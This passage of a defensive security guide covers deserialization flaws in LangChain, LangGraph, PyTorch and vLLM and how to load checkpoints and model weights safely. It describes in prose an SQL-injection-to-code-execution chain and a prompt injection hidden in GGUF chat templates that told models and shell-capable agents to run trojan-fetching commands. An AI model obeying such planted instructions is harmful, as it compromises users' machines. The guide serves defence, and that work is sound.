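| `init_validator` | No check on templates | Blocks Jinja2 templates |

The advisory's migration advice is inconsistent about saved objects for model services, such as `ChatOpenAI`. According to the advisory, these objects will still load without changes, but its definition of `'core'` excludes them. LangChain's current documentation puts such classes under the broader `'all'` setting. Developers who have saved these objects should test some old records before upgrading.

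LangChain's *load* page describes even the new default, `'core'`, as "unsafe with untrusted manifests" and recommends treating a saved object as "executable configuration". For example, a saved chat model can include the address of the server to contact. If a developer allows the chat model's class to be loaded, a forged record can send the agent's requests to an attacker's server.

If a program has to load messages from a source it doesn't trust, it can list the exact classes it needs:

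```python
from langchain_core.load import load
from langchain_core.messages import AIMessage, HumanMessage

messages = load(data, allowed_objects=[AIMessage, HumanMessage])
```

LangChain also offers the setting `allowed_objects="messages"`, which it describes as safe for untrusted input. That description is reasonable with respect to code execution, but the setting also permits `SystemMessage`, the class for the developer's instructions to the model. A forged system message could change how the agent behaves, so the list above excludes that class.

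OSV's *PYSEC-2026-2564* (2026) describes a later LangChain flaw whose risks included forged messages. Three older functions, `RunnableWithMessageHistory`, `astream_log()` and `astream_events(version="v1")`, could still load run data with the broad `'all'` setting instead of the stricter default. Certain dictionaries that resembled secret markers could also avoid the new escaping. LangChain fixed the flaw in langchain-core 0.3.85 and 1.3.3, so these are better minimum versions than 0.3.81 and 1.2.5. It also deprecated the three functions.

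A vulnerability scanner may miss the original flaw in some installations. OSV's record for it lists only versions before 0.3.81, but NVD's *CVE-2025-68664* (2025) page also lists versions from 1.0.0 up to but not including 1.2.5. The JavaScript version of LangChain had a similar flaw, CVE-2025-68665, so a team that uses both needs to upgrade both.

### LangGraph's JSON fallback (CVE-2025-64439)

LangGraph, made by the company behind LangChain, runs agents as a series of steps. Its default serializer, `JsonPlusSerializer`, originally used JSON. LangChain's developers switched it to MessagePack for speed and efficiency, according to LangChain's *Performance enhancements & CI benchmarks for LangGraph Python library*, but the JSON code remained as a fallback.

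LangGraph's serializer fell back to JSON when text contained certain invalid Unicode characters that MessagePack could not save. The JSON loader accepted markers that named a callable and its arguments, and it would import and call whatever a marker named. According to Docker Scout's *CVE-2025-64439* page, which reproduces the advisory, an outsider could exploit this by submitting input that contained such a marker, as long as something in the saved data triggered the fallback. LangGraph saved the input in one run and made the call when it loaded the checkpoint in the next.

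The outsider didn't need access to the database, because LangGraph wrote the dangerous record itself. An application was at risk if it used the default serializer and saved outsiders' input in its checkpoints, as most chat agents do.

The fix, in version 3.0.0 of the langgraph-checkpoint package, stopped the serializer from saving new data as JSON and added an allowlist for loading old JSON records. The stricter loading caused problems for some users. In the LangChain forum post *JsonPlusSerializer does not serialize exceptions*, the developer aecote92 reports that their team's stored Python exceptions no longer loaded as before.

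LangGraph's caches had another fallback, which saved a value as a pickle if MessagePack failed to serialize it, according to OSV's *GHSA-mhr3-j7m5-c7c9* (2026). An attacker needed write access to the cache to exploit this, and caching is off by default. Version 4.0.0 of langgraph-checkpoint turned the fallback off.

### LangGraph's MessagePack hook (CVE-2026-28277)

LangGraph's MessagePack hook could also call arbitrary functions. For one of its extension types, it did the following:

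1. It decoded the extension's bytes into a module name, the name of something in that module, and an argument.
2. It imported the module.
3. It looked up the name in the module.
4. It called the result with the argument.

Given `builtins`, `len` and `Oslo`, the hook would call `len("Oslo")` and return 4. It accepted any module and function name. It also discarded any error, so a failed attempt might leave nothing in the logs.

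LangGraph needed the hook for rebuilding objects, but like pickle's REDUCE opcode, it worked with any callable.

Unlike the JSON fallback, this flaw required an attacker to control the saved bytes. A user could send a table that looked like an extension, but LangGraph would save it as a table. The maintainers therefore described it as "defense-in-depth". They argue in their advisory (GCVE, *GHSA-G48C-2WQR-H844*, 2026) that anyone who can change stored checkpoints has usually already caused a serious incident. They knew of no attacks and no practical way to exploit the flaw in existing deployments.

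### How a search field could supply a forged checkpoint

Yarden Porat, who had also reported the LangChain flaw, found a way to supply a forged checkpoint without changing the database. In *From SQLi to RCE*, an article for the security company Check Point, Porat (2026) combines the MessagePack flaw with an SQL injection flaw, CVE-2025-67644. SQL injection lets an outsider's input become part of a database query instead of being treated as a value.

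1. An application lets users search an agent's history by metadata, such as a user name or step number. It passes their search to LangGraph's `get_state_history()` function.
2. LangGraph's SQLite checkpointer (the component that stores checkpoints in an SQLite database) handles the search values safely but inserts the field names directly into the query.
3. An attacker sends a crafted field name that adds an invented row to the query's results. The row contains a forged checkpoint.
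4. The checkpointer deserializes every row it gets back, and the hook makes the call in the forged one.

The forged checkpoint exists only in the query's results, so a read-only database account would not have stopped the attack, and an audit of the stored records would not have found it.

A deployment was exposed only if the application ran on the developer's own server, used the SQLite checkpointer and let outsiders choose the names of search fields. Many applications probably let users choose only the values, or don't offer such a search. LangChain's hosted service was not exposed because it uses PostgreSQL. Porat found the same kind of injection in LangGraph's Redis checkpointer (CVE-2026-27022) but explains the full attack only for SQLite.

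OSV's *GHSA-9rwj-6rc7-p77c* (2025), the maintainers' advisory on the SQL injection, suggests that users who can choose field names probably already have permission to query the checkpoint database, but that permission would not normally let them run code on the server. The advisory's severity score of 7.3 covers only the injection, not the combined attack.

Porat reported both flaws on 19 November 2025. LangChain fixed the SQL injection on 10 December, which broke the chain, and published the advisory on the MessagePack hook the following March. The maintainers' statement that they knew of no practical route was therefore reasonable for servers with the December fix, but too reassuring for anyone still running the older SQLite package.

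The maintainers were right that an attacker needs another flaw or stolen access to exploit the hook. But SQL injection and leaked database passwords are common enough that developers should plan for them. If the hook is unsafe, either one can also give the attacker the agent's API keys and access to other systems.

### The patch and the default of `LANGGRAPH_STRICT_MSGPACK`

A patch for CVE-2026-28277 has been available since 5 March 2026, although OSV's *CVE-2026-28277* (2026) page still read "No known patch is public" after an update in late October 2026. GCVE lists langgraph 1.0.10 as the fixed version, while Porat lists langgraph-checkpoint 4.0.1. The two version numbers differ because LangGraph consists of several packages, and the serializer is in langgraph-checkpoint.

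But installing the patch is not enough, because the strict mode it added is **off by default**. LangChain's *langgraph-checkpoint 4.3.2* (2026) page, for a release from 14 November, states that the serializer still "allows any Python type found in checkpoint data" by default. It advises developers of new applications to set `LANGGRAPH_STRICT_MSGPACK=true` or provide their own list of permitted types.

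The serializer's `allowed_msgpack_modules` setting controls the same behaviour:

| Value | What the loader does |
|---|---|
| `True` (default) | Rebuilds any type, with a warning if the type isn't registered |
| `None` (default in strict mode) | Rebuilds only a built-in set of types, such as dates, sets, decimals and file paths |
| A list of module and class names | Rebuilds the built-in set and the listed classes |

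A developer who needs to save `Reading` objects can list that class:

```python
from langgraph.checkpoint.serde.jsonplus import JsonPlusSerializer

serializer = JsonPlusSerializer(
    allowed_msgpack_modules=[("weather", "Reading")])
```

The checkpointer then has to use this serializer. Developers often don't need to write the list by hand, because in strict mode LangGraph builds it from the declared types of the agent's state and adds common LangChain message classes.

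Strict mode has gaps. If a checkpointer from another company doesn't support the automatic list, LangGraph may give a warning and skip the restriction. A custom `ext_hook` can also bypass the restriction. MongoDB's *Upgrade API used for serialization to allow input of allowed_json_modules* shows that developers once could not pass such settings to the serializer through MongoDB's checkpointer, though MongoDB has since marked the request as done.

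A mistyped variable name leaves strict mode off without an error. *How to register type in langgraph* (sog) describes a developer who set `LANGCHAIN_ALLOWED_MSGPACK_MODULES`, which doesn't exist, and wondered why the warnings continued. According to the warnings, a future version would block unregistered types, but version 4.3.2 still allowed them. LangGraph reads the real variable when Python imports the library, so the variable is best set before the program starts.

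A simple test of strict mode is to save an object of an unlisted class and try to load it. If the object comes back intact, strict mode isn't working.

### Old JSON checkpoints (CVE-2026-48775)

LangGraph's JSON loader was found to be unsafe a second time. On 16 June 2026, OSV's *CVE-2026-48775* (2026) record described how a forged JSON checkpoint could lead to code execution in langgraph-checkpoint versions up to 4.1.0. A researcher from the security company CyStack reported the vulnerability. Five days before the record, Porat had written that LangGraph's JSON format did not lead to code execution.

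The loader still accepted JSON so that users could resume runs from before the move to MessagePack. A record could also specify a way to build an object other than the class's normal constructor. New LangGraph checkpoints had not needed this since the move, according to the advisory in Positive Technologies' *PT-2026-59230* (2026). Version 4.1.1 allows only the normal constructor.

LangGraph no longer writes JSON checkpoints itself, so an attacker needs write access to the checkpoint store, or an equivalent such as the SQL injection above. `LANGGRAPH_STRICT_MSGPACK` applies only to MessagePack, so setting it does not replace this upgrade.

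The LangGraph fixes are spread over several packages:

| Flaw | First fixed version | Further action |
|---|---|---|
| JSON fallback (CVE-2025-64439) | langgraph-checkpoint 3.0.0 | None |
| SQL injection in SQLite (CVE-2025-67644) | langgraph-checkpoint-sqlite 3.0.1 | None |
| SQL injection in Redis (CVE-2026-27022) | langgraph-checkpoint-redis 1.0.2 | None |
| Pickle fallback in caches | langgraph-checkpoint 4.0.0 | None |
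| MessagePack hook (CVE-2026-28277) | langgraph-checkpoint 4.0.1 | Turn on strict mode or list the permitted classes |
| Old JSON checkpoints (CVE-2026-48775) | langgraph-checkpoint 4.1.1 | None |

Upgrading only the main `langgraph` package may leave an old checkpointer in place. `pip list` shows the version of each package.

### Saving state as plain data

Developers who write their own storage can avoid markers altogether. The following code saves a conversation as plain JSON, checks it against a simple schema and then creates the objects itself:

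```python
import json
from dataclasses import asdict, dataclass

@dataclass
class Message:
    role: str
    text: str

def save(messages):
    return json.dumps({"version": 2,
                       "messages": [asdict(m) for m in messages]})

def to_message(item):
    if not isinstance(item, dict) or set(item) != {"role", "text"}:
        raise ValueError("unexpected fields")
    if item["role"] not in ("user", "assistant"):
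        raise ValueError("unknown role")
    if not isinstance(item["text"], str):
        raise ValueError("message must be text")
    return Message(**item)

def restore(raw):
    record = json.loads(raw)
    if not isinstance(record, dict) or \
            not isinstance(record.get("messages"), list):
        raise ValueError("not a saved conversation")
    items = record["messages"]
    if record.get("version") == 1:
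        # Version 1 stored only the user's texts
        items = [{"role": "user", "text": t} for t in items]
    elif record.get("version") != 2:
        raise ValueError("unknown version")
    return [to_message(item) for item in items]
```

No value in the record can select a class. The program loads every item in `messages` as a `Message`, so an `lc` or `$type` key is an unexpected field and causes an error. The code also rejects system messages, because the developer's instructions should come from the program and not from a saved conversation.

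Python's `json` module can also save the invalid Unicode characters that triggered LangGraph's fallback. If a serializer fails on some data, raising an error is safer than switching to a more powerful format.

This approach works well for messages and simple settings. It takes more work for an agent with dozens of state classes, where a framework's serializer with an explicit allowlist may be more practical. That allowlist needs the same care as one for pickle. LangChain's Bedrock class was on an allowlist but still sent a web request.

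### Escaping reserved keys

A format that uses markers to represent objects must escape every dictionary that comes from outside, and the loader must process the escapes in the right order. With `object_hook`, Python's `json` module processes inner dictionaries before outer ones, so the hook may build an object from an outsider's dictionary before it reaches the surrounding escape wrapper. A safer loader parses the whole text into plain data and then works from the outside in. LangChain's current `loads` function also parses the text first and then passes the result to `load`.

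A round-trip test can catch a missing escape. This one uses an ordinary dictionary that looks like a LangChain message:

```python
from langchain_core.load import dumps, loads

def test_table_stays_a_table():
    data = {
        "lc": 1,
        "type": "constructor",
        "id": ["langchain", "schema", "messages", "AIMessage"],
        "kwargs": {"content": "Hello"},
    }
    assert loads(dumps(data)) == data
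```

If the escape is missing, `loads` returns an `AIMessage` instead of the dictionary, and the test fails. A similar test for each kind of marker would be useful, because LangChain's first fix missed some dictionaries that resembled secrets.

### Who can write to the store

An agent may be able to change its own checkpoints. For example, its database query tool might use the same database account as the checkpointer. An outsider who can steer the model could then have it write a forged checkpoint, which the host process would load on the next run. The same problem can arise if a file-saving tool can write to the folder that contains the SQLite database.

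The checkpointer should therefore have its own database account, and the agent's tools should have no access to the checkpoint tables. In a service with many users, users should be able to load only their own threads (LangGraph's name for a series of checkpoints). If someone may have had unauthorized access to the store, LangGraph's maintainers recommend replacing its credentials. It also makes sense to stop loading checkpoints from that period.

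Neither restricted access nor signatures fix a missing escape, because the application itself writes the dangerous record and would sign it too.

### Migrating old records

Upgrading LangChain does not change the records already in the database. Records saved before the fix have no escapes, so a table supplied by an outsider may still look like a LangChain object. The new loader's stricter defaults limit what it will do with such a table, but converting or deleting the old records is safer.

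1. Delete whatever the agent can recreate or no longer needs, such as caches and the checkpoints of finished runs.
2. Find out which classes the remaining records need. LangGraph's warnings about unregistered types give their names. This has to happen on a copy of the data, in an isolated environment without credentials, because loading in the permissive mode can run code.
3. Load the records with an allowlist of those classes, and save them in the new format with a version number.
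4. Check the type of each restored value as well as looking for errors.
5. Remove the code that reads the old format.

Step 4 matters because LangGraph doesn't always raise an error when it can't rebuild an object. In strict mode, values of unlisted classes come back as plain dictionaries, according to *Wire allowed_msgpack_modules in langgraph.json*, a feature request on LangChain's forum. The program may then fail much later, when it uses a dictionary as if it were the original object. The fix for CVE-2026-48775 has a similar effect on objects from the validation library Pydantic in some checkpoints from before October 2025, if the objects' class definitions have changed since.

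LangGraph's JSON loader was still exploitable long after the framework switched to MessagePack, yet developers often skip step 5 because the old reader seems harmless once nothing uses it. If some users need to resume old runs for a while, the old reader can run in a separate conversion program, outside the agent's host process.

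## Loading model weights without running code

A trained model's weights are only numbers, so loading them shouldn't require any objects or function calls. But many weights files are pickles, because PyTorch, the library that developers use for most models, saves them that way by default. An agent tool that downloads and loads a model may therefore run a stranger's code before it uses the model.

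A developer has four options, listed here from safest to riskiest:

| Option | When to use it | Main remaining risk |
|---|---|---|
| A data-only file, such as safetensors | Whenever the model comes in one | Bugs in the loader, and other files in the repository |
| `torch.load` with `weights_only=True` | The only weights file is a pickle of ordinary weights | Bugs, especially in older PyTorch versions |
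| An allowlist for one library's models | The pickle needs a few more classes | Misuse of the permitted callables |
| A scan, then loading in isolation | Nothing else can load the file | An attack that the scan misses and the isolation doesn't contain |

### What a safetensors file contains

Hugging Face released safetensors in September 2022 as a safer alternative to pickle. The format stores only tensors, which are arrays of numbers with any number of dimensions. A file has three parts, according to docs.rs' *Crate safetensors*:

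1. Eight bytes give the length of the header.
2. The header is JSON text with each tensor's name, number type, shape and position.
3. The rest of the file contains the numbers.

A file that holds three temperatures could have this header:

```json
{"temps":{"dtype":"F32","shape":[3],"data_offsets":[0,12]}}
```

`F32` means 32-bit numbers, which take four bytes each, so the data runs from byte 0 to byte 12. The header is 59 characters long, and the library pads it with spaces to 64. The file is therefore 8 + 64 + 12 = 84 bytes long. To load it, a program parses the JSON and copies the numbers into an array. No field in the header can select a class or function.

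The loader still has to check the header, because an unchecked false position could make it read the wrong part of memory. Trail of Bits' *EleutherAI Security Assessment* (2023), an audit of an early version, found that the library did not compare tensor positions with the total size of the data, and that its size calculations could overflow. The newer source code on docs.rs defines errors for both problems. It requires the tensors to cover the data completely, with the last one ending where the file ends. The loader also rejects headers larger than 100 MB, according to PyTorch's *Safetensors* page.

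A tool can load such a file like this:

```python
from safetensors.torch import load_file

def load_weights(path):
    model = RainModel()                     # class from the program
    model.load_state_dict(load_file(path))  # numbers from the file
    return model
```

`load_state_dict` raises an error if the tensor names or shapes don't match the model. `load_file` fails on a pickle renamed to `model.safetensors` because it reads the first eight bytes as a header length.

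Loading a repository with safetensors weights can still run code. Many repositories also keep a pickle of the same weights for older programs, and a tool may load the pickle instead. In Hugging Face's Transformers library, passing `use_safetensors=True` to `from_pretrained` makes it accept only safetensors weights. Even with safe weights, remote model code or settings that reach Hydra's `instantiate` function can run code.

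### GGUF files and their chat templates

People who run language models on their own computers mostly use GGUF, a format from August 2023. A GGUF file contains a header, a table of metadata, a table of tensors, some padding and the weights, in that order. Programs such as llama.cpp, an open-source engine for running models, read only the parts that these tables point to.

The metadata usually includes a **chat template**, a small program in the template language Jinja2 that turns a conversation into the model's input text. Engines written in C++ run the template without Python, so it can't call Python functions. A Python program that renders the template needs Jinja2's sandboxed mode.

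Even a restricted template can add text to the conversation that the user never sees. *GGUF LLM Models with Hidden Malware on Hugging Face Reached 2400+ Victims* (Düzgün, 2026) describes a scan of all 3,273,389 public model repositories on Hugging Face that found five malicious GGUF models. In two of them, the template contained an instruction for the model to start its answers with a command for the user to run, which would start a Windows trojan stored after the last tensor in the file. Other templates responded to a trigger phrase by inserting a false system instruction for agents with shell access to download and run a script.

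Loading these files did not run any code. The attack was a prompt injection inside the model file, and it needed a person or an agent to run the command. The five models had 2,428 downloads, possibly by fewer people. Faisal (2026), in *Five Malicious AI Models on Hugging Face Hid a Windows Trojan*, counts 226,310 GGUF repositories in the same scan, so about one in 45,000 was malicious.

Safetensors would have prevented only half of this method. Its loader rejects files with extra bytes at the end, but models in that format have the same kind of chat template in a separate file. A developer can read the template before using a model, or replace it with the one from the model's original publisher. The attacker uploaded the two trojan models on 22 and 24 November and changed their templates on the 26th, so a check on the day of upload would have found harmless templates. Downloading one fixed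 revision and checking that copy is safer.

### How `torch.load` restricts a pickle

PyTorch's `torch.save` writes a ZIP archive. Each tensor's values go into a separate file in the `data` folder, and a pickle called `data.pkl` describes how to put everything together, according to PyTorch's *Serialization semantics*.

Ideally, the pickle contains only a state dict, which is a dictionary that maps parameter names to tensors. The program then creates the model from a class in its own code, as `load_weights` does. If someone saves the whole model object instead, the pickle also has to name the model's class and every class used inside the model.

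With `weights_only=True`, `torch.load` uses PyTorch's own restricted unpickler, which works like the `find_class` override in the pickle section, with a built-in allowlist. According to *Add `weights_only` option to `torch.load`*, the description of the original change, the allowlist includes plain values, lists, tuples, dictionaries and PyTorch's types for tensors, parameters and sizes. The unpickler never imports modules named in the file.

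PyTorch introduced this option in version 1.13, in November 2022, but left it off by default. It became the default in version 2.6, around the start of 2025. What a call does therefore depends on the version as well as the arguments:

| Call | PyTorch 1.13 to 2.5 | PyTorch 2.6 and later |
|---|---|---|
| `torch.load(path)` | Loads any pickle | Restricted |
| `torch.load(path, weights_only=True)` | Restricted, but with a critical flaw | Restricted |
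| `torch.load(path, weights_only=False)` | Loads any pickle | Loads any pickle |
| `torch.load(path, pickle_module=pickle)` | Loads any pickle | Loads any pickle |

`weights_only=True` is worth writing explicitly, in case the code ever runs with an older version of PyTorch. Bandit's *B614* rule flags unsafe `torch.load` calls in a team's own code.

For calls inside installed packages, a developer can set the environment variable `TORCH_FORCE_WEIGHTS_ONLY_LOAD=1`, which imposes the restriction on every `torch.load` call in the process. Another variable, `TORCH_FORCE_NO_WEIGHTS_ONLY_LOAD=1`, removes the restriction from calls that don't set `weights_only`. An audit should check that no container image or start-up script sets this second variable.

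If an old pickle contains only a state dict, a developer can convert it once:

```python
import torch
from safetensors.torch import save_file

state = torch.load("model.pth", weights_only=True, map_location="cpu")
state = {name: t.clone().contiguous() for name, t in state.items()}
save_file(state, "model.safetensors")
```

The second-to-last line makes a separate copy of each tensor, because safetensors doesn't store tensors that share memory. The agent can then use the safetensors file, and nobody has to load the pickle again.

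### Allowing a few more classes

When a file needs a callable that isn't on the allowlist, `torch.load` raises an error with two suggested fixes. One is to set `weights_only=False`, which comes with a warning that this can run arbitrary code, and the other is to extend the allowlist. A developer in a hurry, or a coding agent trying to clear the error, could easily choose the first because it almost always works.

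PyTorch's documentation also recommends `weights_only=False` for old files that contain a whole model object. That setting is reasonable for a team's own files, but it allows a file from outside to run code on loading.

Suppose someone has saved a `Reading` object along with the weights. PyTorch can list the missing names without loading the file, and then permit the class for one load:

```python
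import torch
from weather import Reading

print(torch.serialization.get_unsafe_globals_in_checkpoint("model.pt"))
# ['weather.Reading']

with torch.serialization.safe_globals([Reading]):
    data = torch.load("model.pt", weights_only=True)
```

("Checkpoint" here means a weights file, not an agent checkpoint.)

The `with` block is safer than `add_safe_globals`, which permits the class for the rest of the process. The list of missing names can be incomplete because some types appear only during loading. For example, loading a file that contains NumPy data may raise a second error after the developer has permitted everything on the list.

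As with any pickle allowlist, a developer should read the code each name refers to before adding it, because whoever made the file still chooses the arguments and the saved state.

### Why the PyTorch version matters

Before April 2025, the standard advice for loading untrusted weights was to set `weights_only=True`, which PyTorch's own security page described as safe. Ji'an Zhou then showed that a crafted file could run code despite the setting. OSV's *PyTorch* (2025) record rates this flaw, CVE-2025-32434, as critical and lists every version before 2.6.0 as affected. Version 2.6.0 fixes the flaw and makes `weights_only=True` the default, so there is little reason to accept an older version.

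Zhou found a second flaw, CVE-2026-24747. The restricted unpickler did not check that steps for filling a dictionary applied to a dictionary, or that a tensor's declared size matched the data in the archive. A crafted file could corrupt the program's memory and potentially run code that way. OSV's *PyTorch Vulnerable to Remote Code Execution via Untrusted Checkpoint Files* (2026) scores it 8.8 and lists version 2.10.0 as the fix.

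A dependency scanner that relies only on OSV's record of this second flaw would not report it in PyTorch 2.9. The record lists the affected package as `pytorch`, with only versions 0.1.2 and 1.0.2, but developers install PyTorch as `torch`. Printing `torch.__version__` is a more reliable check.

More flaws of the second kind are likely. An allowlist controls which callables a pickle can reach, but PyTorch still builds tensors, largely in C++ code, using sizes and positions from an untrusted file. According to PyTorch's documentation, memory corruption "might still be possible" with `weights_only=True`, and the option doesn't prevent a file from using up time or memory.

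### Tensors inside requests to vLLM

The documentation also warns that a file can load without any problem and then cause memory corruption in the code that uses it. This happened in vLLM, an inference server. A vLLM client can send a prompt as embeddings, which are the numbers that a model computes from text, instead of as text. vLLM expected them in PyTorch's file format. According to OSV's *vLLM deserialization vulnerability leading to DoS and potential RCE*, it did the following:

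1. It loaded the data with `weights_only=True`.
2. It checked that the result was a tensor with a permitted number type.
3. It called the tensor's `to_dense()` method.

The third step was the dangerous one. A **sparse tensor** stores only the nonzero values and their positions. For example, the list `[0, 0, 7, 0]` becomes a 7 at position 2 in a list of length 4. `to_dense()` creates the full list and writes each value into its place. If the data gives a position beyond the end of the list and nothing checks it, `to_dense()` writes the value elsewhere in the server's memory. This can crash the server and may let an attacker run code.

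The flaw, CVE-2025-62164, affected version 0.10.2 onward. Anyone with access to the API could send such a tensor. NVD's *CVE-2025-62164* (2025) page classifies the flaw as both unsafe deserialization and an out-of-bounds write.

vLLM's developers needed three attempts to fix it:

| Version | Change |
|---|---|
| 0.11.1 | Turned off prompt embeddings by default |
| 0.13.0 | Added the missing check of positions |
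| 0.26.0 | Made the check work when several tensors arrive at once |

OSV's *vLLM introduced enhanced protection for CVE-2025-62164* (2026) explains that the first change left the flaw in place for anyone who turned the feature back on. The later problem arose because PyTorch's check is a process-wide setting. When vLLM handled several tensors at once, finishing one could turn off the check before another had gone through it. OSV's *vLLM* (2026) record scores this remaining flaw at only 6.3, which assumes a limited effect on the server's availability.

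OSV's records disagree about when PyTorch stopped checking sparse tensors by default. One gives version 2.8.0 and another gives roughly 2.0. A tool that doesn't need sparse tensors can avoid the question by refusing them:

```python
tensor = torch.load(file, weights_only=True, map_location="cpu")
if not isinstance(tensor, torch.Tensor) or tensor.layout != torch.strided:
    raise ValueError("expected an ordinary tensor")
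```

`torch.strided` is PyTorch's name for the ordinary tensor layout. Accepting safetensors in requests would be better still, because that format doesn't support sparse tensors.

Software that avoids pickle can still have flaws that let attackers run code. In November 2026, the security firm VulnCheck disclosed such a flaw in llama.cpp's optional server for spreading a model across several machines. Faisal's *Critical llama.cpp Flaw Lets Attackers Run Code on AI Servers* (2026) explains that a tensor with no elements made the server skip a bounds check, so a copy could then write outside the permitted memory. The flaw has a severity score of 9.8 and is fixed in build b12658. Programs that accept tensors from untrusted sources need prompt updates, whatever file format they use.

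### How many models still depend on pickle

In March 2025, Kellas and colleagues surveyed 16,661 Hugging Face repositories with at least 1,000 downloads a month. They found pickle files in 44.9% of them, or about 7,480.

Far fewer repositories than that need pickle. Many also had the same weights in safetensors, and some pickle files held only training settings. The researchers identified formats by file extension, which is approximate. They put the share of repositories with only pickle models at 21%, although the 4,553 such repositories they mention elsewhere would be 27% of the total. The pickle-only models had over 400 million downloads a month and included 29 of the 100 most downloaded models.

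The survey is 21 months old, and Hugging Face has grown from about 1.8 million models in July 2025 to nearly 3.3 million public repositories, so the shares could be quite different now. The major open language models of early 2025, such as Llama 4 and Qwen 3, already came as safetensors, but people who shared adapted versions often added a pickle file.

Kellas and colleagues also checked how many pickle-only models the weights-only unpickler would accept. They could analyse 1,426 of the 1,500 most popular repositories. In 219 of them (15.4%), at least one model needed a callable that the default allowlist doesn't permit. Those 219 repositories had 79.6 million downloads in a month. The other 1,207 should work with `weights_only=True` without further effort.

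The 219 repositories needed only 36 different callables in total, many from NumPy and Transformers, so a team that uses a few of these models would probably have a short list to review.

But some libraries turn the restriction off for their users. Flair, a text-analysis library, loads its models with `weights_only=False` because they need classes outside the default list. Upgrading PyTorch doesn't protect someone who loads a stranger's model through Flair. Searching the installed packages for `weights_only=False` finds such cases.

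### How PickleBall builds an allowlist

PickleBall automates the third option. Its basic idea is that a legitimate file only needs calls that help rebuild an object of the model's class, and the library's source code for that class shows which calls those are.

Suppose a library defines this class:

```python
class Forecaster:
    def __init__(self, latest: Reading, weights: Tensor):
        self.latest = latest
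        self.weights = weights
```

PickleBall analyses the source code without running it and produces two lists. One contains the names that a file may look up, and the other contains the callables that it may call. The analysis goes like this:

1. `Forecaster` has no `__reduce__` method, so PickleBall adds it to the lookup list. It then puts the class's subclasses and the types of its attributes, `Reading` and `Tensor`, in a queue.
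2. `Reading` has no `__reduce__` method either, so it also goes on the lookup list. Its attributes are plain values.
3. `Tensor` has a `__reduce__` method that returns a function, `rebuild`. PickleBall adds `rebuild` to both lists and queues the types of its arguments.
4. The analysis ends when the queue is empty.

A file can then create instances of `Forecaster` and `Reading`, but the only function it can call is `rebuild`.

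Python code doesn't always reveal its types, so the lists can be incomplete. PickleBall deals with this through **lazy enforcement**. If a file refers to a name that isn't on the list, the loader substitutes a harmless stand-in object and continues. The stand-in raises a security error as soon as anything tries to call or use it. For example, a file may include training details that the program never uses. An ordinary allowlist would reject the whole file because of them, but PickleBall can still load it.

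If a malicious file looks up `builtins.len` and calls it, the lookup yields a stand-in and the call fails.

Kellas and colleagues tested PickleBall on 252 benign models from 16 libraries. It loaded 201 of them (79.8%), and each loaded model gave the same result on a test input as it did when loaded with ordinary pickle. The weights-only unpickler loaded 157 (62.3%).

That advantage came entirely from four libraries (flair, PyAnnote, YOLOv5 and YOLOv11). The weights-only unpickler rejected all 95 of their models, and PickleBall loaded 46 of them. For the other 12 libraries, the weights-only unpickler loaded every model, while PickleBall failed on two. PickleBall is therefore worth considering only for models that the simpler weights-only unpickler rejects.

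YOLO models accounted for 44 of PickleBall's 51 failures. Their files sometimes referred to a class by a shorter module name than the one in the library, so the names didn't match the list. A developer could probably fix many of these cases by hand.

PickleBall also blocked all 84 malicious files in the test. Analysing a library took a median of 14 seconds and only has to be repeated when the library changes. Loading took 2.62% longer on average than with the version of pickle written in Python. Programs normally use a faster version written in C, so the real slowdown would be larger, but the researchers didn't measure it.

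The lists are also much longer than the models need. They permit 767 to 1,816 lookups and 61 to 64 calls, while the models in the test used at most 63 lookups and 11 calls. The extra entries give an attacker more code to misuse, although Kellas and colleagues knew of no such attack.

The researchers also had to edit the source code of five of the 16 libraries, changing about 10 to 100 lines in each, before the tool's analysis worked. The tool relies on the library being trustworthy and on the developer knowing which class to expect. For a team that uses one or two unusual models, PyTorch's `safe_globals` is probably simpler.

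### Malicious weights files on Hugging Face

Attackers upload malicious pickles to public repositories. The security company Rapid7 found several in one suspicious Hugging Face account. Rapid7's *From .pth to p0wned* describes how loading them with `torch.load` ran commands that downloaded a remote access trojan, a program that lets an attacker control the machine. In one case, the trojan was in the same repository as the pickles.

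The files were too small to be convincing as models. Two were 495 bytes and a third was 1,583 bytes, while even a small model's weights usually take up megabytes. A person who looked at the file sizes might have become suspicious, and Hugging Face was already showing a warning, but an agent that loads a model by name may check neither. Rapid7 doesn't report how many people downloaded the files.

The weights-only unpickler should have rejected these files, since its allowlist includes no function for starting programs. They were mainly a danger to people using older PyTorch versions or code that turns the restriction off.

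Rapid7's case was one of many. Of the 84 malicious files in the PickleBall test, 82 came from Hugging Face, where earlier researchers had found them. Kellas and colleagues cite a study that found the rate of malicious uploads had risen fivefold in a year, and they report that almost all malicious models on the site used pickle. Düzgün's more recent scan doesn't show whether that has changed, because it looked for malicious GGUF files.

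### What scanners check

Most model scanners automate what a reviewer does with pickletools. They list the callables that a pickle would look up and compare them with a denylist. Hugging Face runs such a scanner and shows the results on each model's page. Other scanners load the file and monitor what it does, so they have to run in isolation.

Kellas and colleagues tested one scanner of each kind on the same files as PickleBall. ModelScan uses a denylist, and ModelTracer watches the file while it loads:

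| Tool | Malicious files caught or blocked (of 84) | Benign models accepted (of 252) |
|---|---|---|
| ModelScan | 75 | 236 |
| ModelTracer | 44 | 252 |
| Weights-only unpickler | 84 | 157 |
| PickleBall | 84 | 201 |

ModelScan missed nine malicious files and raised 16 false alarms. Five of the nine used callables that weren't on its denylist. Adding those callables would help only until someone used another unlisted one. ModelTracer missed 40 of the malicious files, nearly half, because it treats only four kinds of system call as suspicious.

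The scanners would probably do worse in practice. Nearly all the malicious files were ones that some scanner had already found, so the test contains few of the attacks that scanners tend to miss. Researchers have also built malicious files that evade current scanners.

Scanners also raise false alarms. Hugging Face's scanner warned about suspicious imports in a flair model with over a million downloads. Kellas and colleagues read the model's pickle and flair's source code and concluded that the model was benign. Most users won't do that much work, and they may learn to ignore the warnings.

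A scan is still an easy way to reject known attacks such as Rapid7's, but a clean result doesn't justify loading a pickle without restrictions in the host process. If a tool needs a model that only an unrestricted loader can open, the loader should run in a sandbox without credentials, as PyTorch's *SECURITY.md* also suggests for untrusted models. Often it has to run only once, to convert the weights to safetensors. The host process can then load the new file using a model class from its own code.

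## Deciding whether a model repository may run its own code

A program that loads a model needs both the weights and the code that arranges them into layers and calculates with them. For a new kind of model, that code often comes from the model's own repository. In Hugging Face's Transformers library, the setting `trust_remote_code=True` allows the repository's code to run, so whoever controls the repository can run Python on any machine that loads the model this way.

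### What happens when a repository supplies code

Suppose a repository contains a rainfall model with a new design. Its `config.json` could include these lines:

```json
{
  "model_type": "rain",
  "auto_map": {
    "AutoConfig": "configuration_rain.RainConfig",
    "AutoModel": "modeling_rain.RainModel"
  }
}
```

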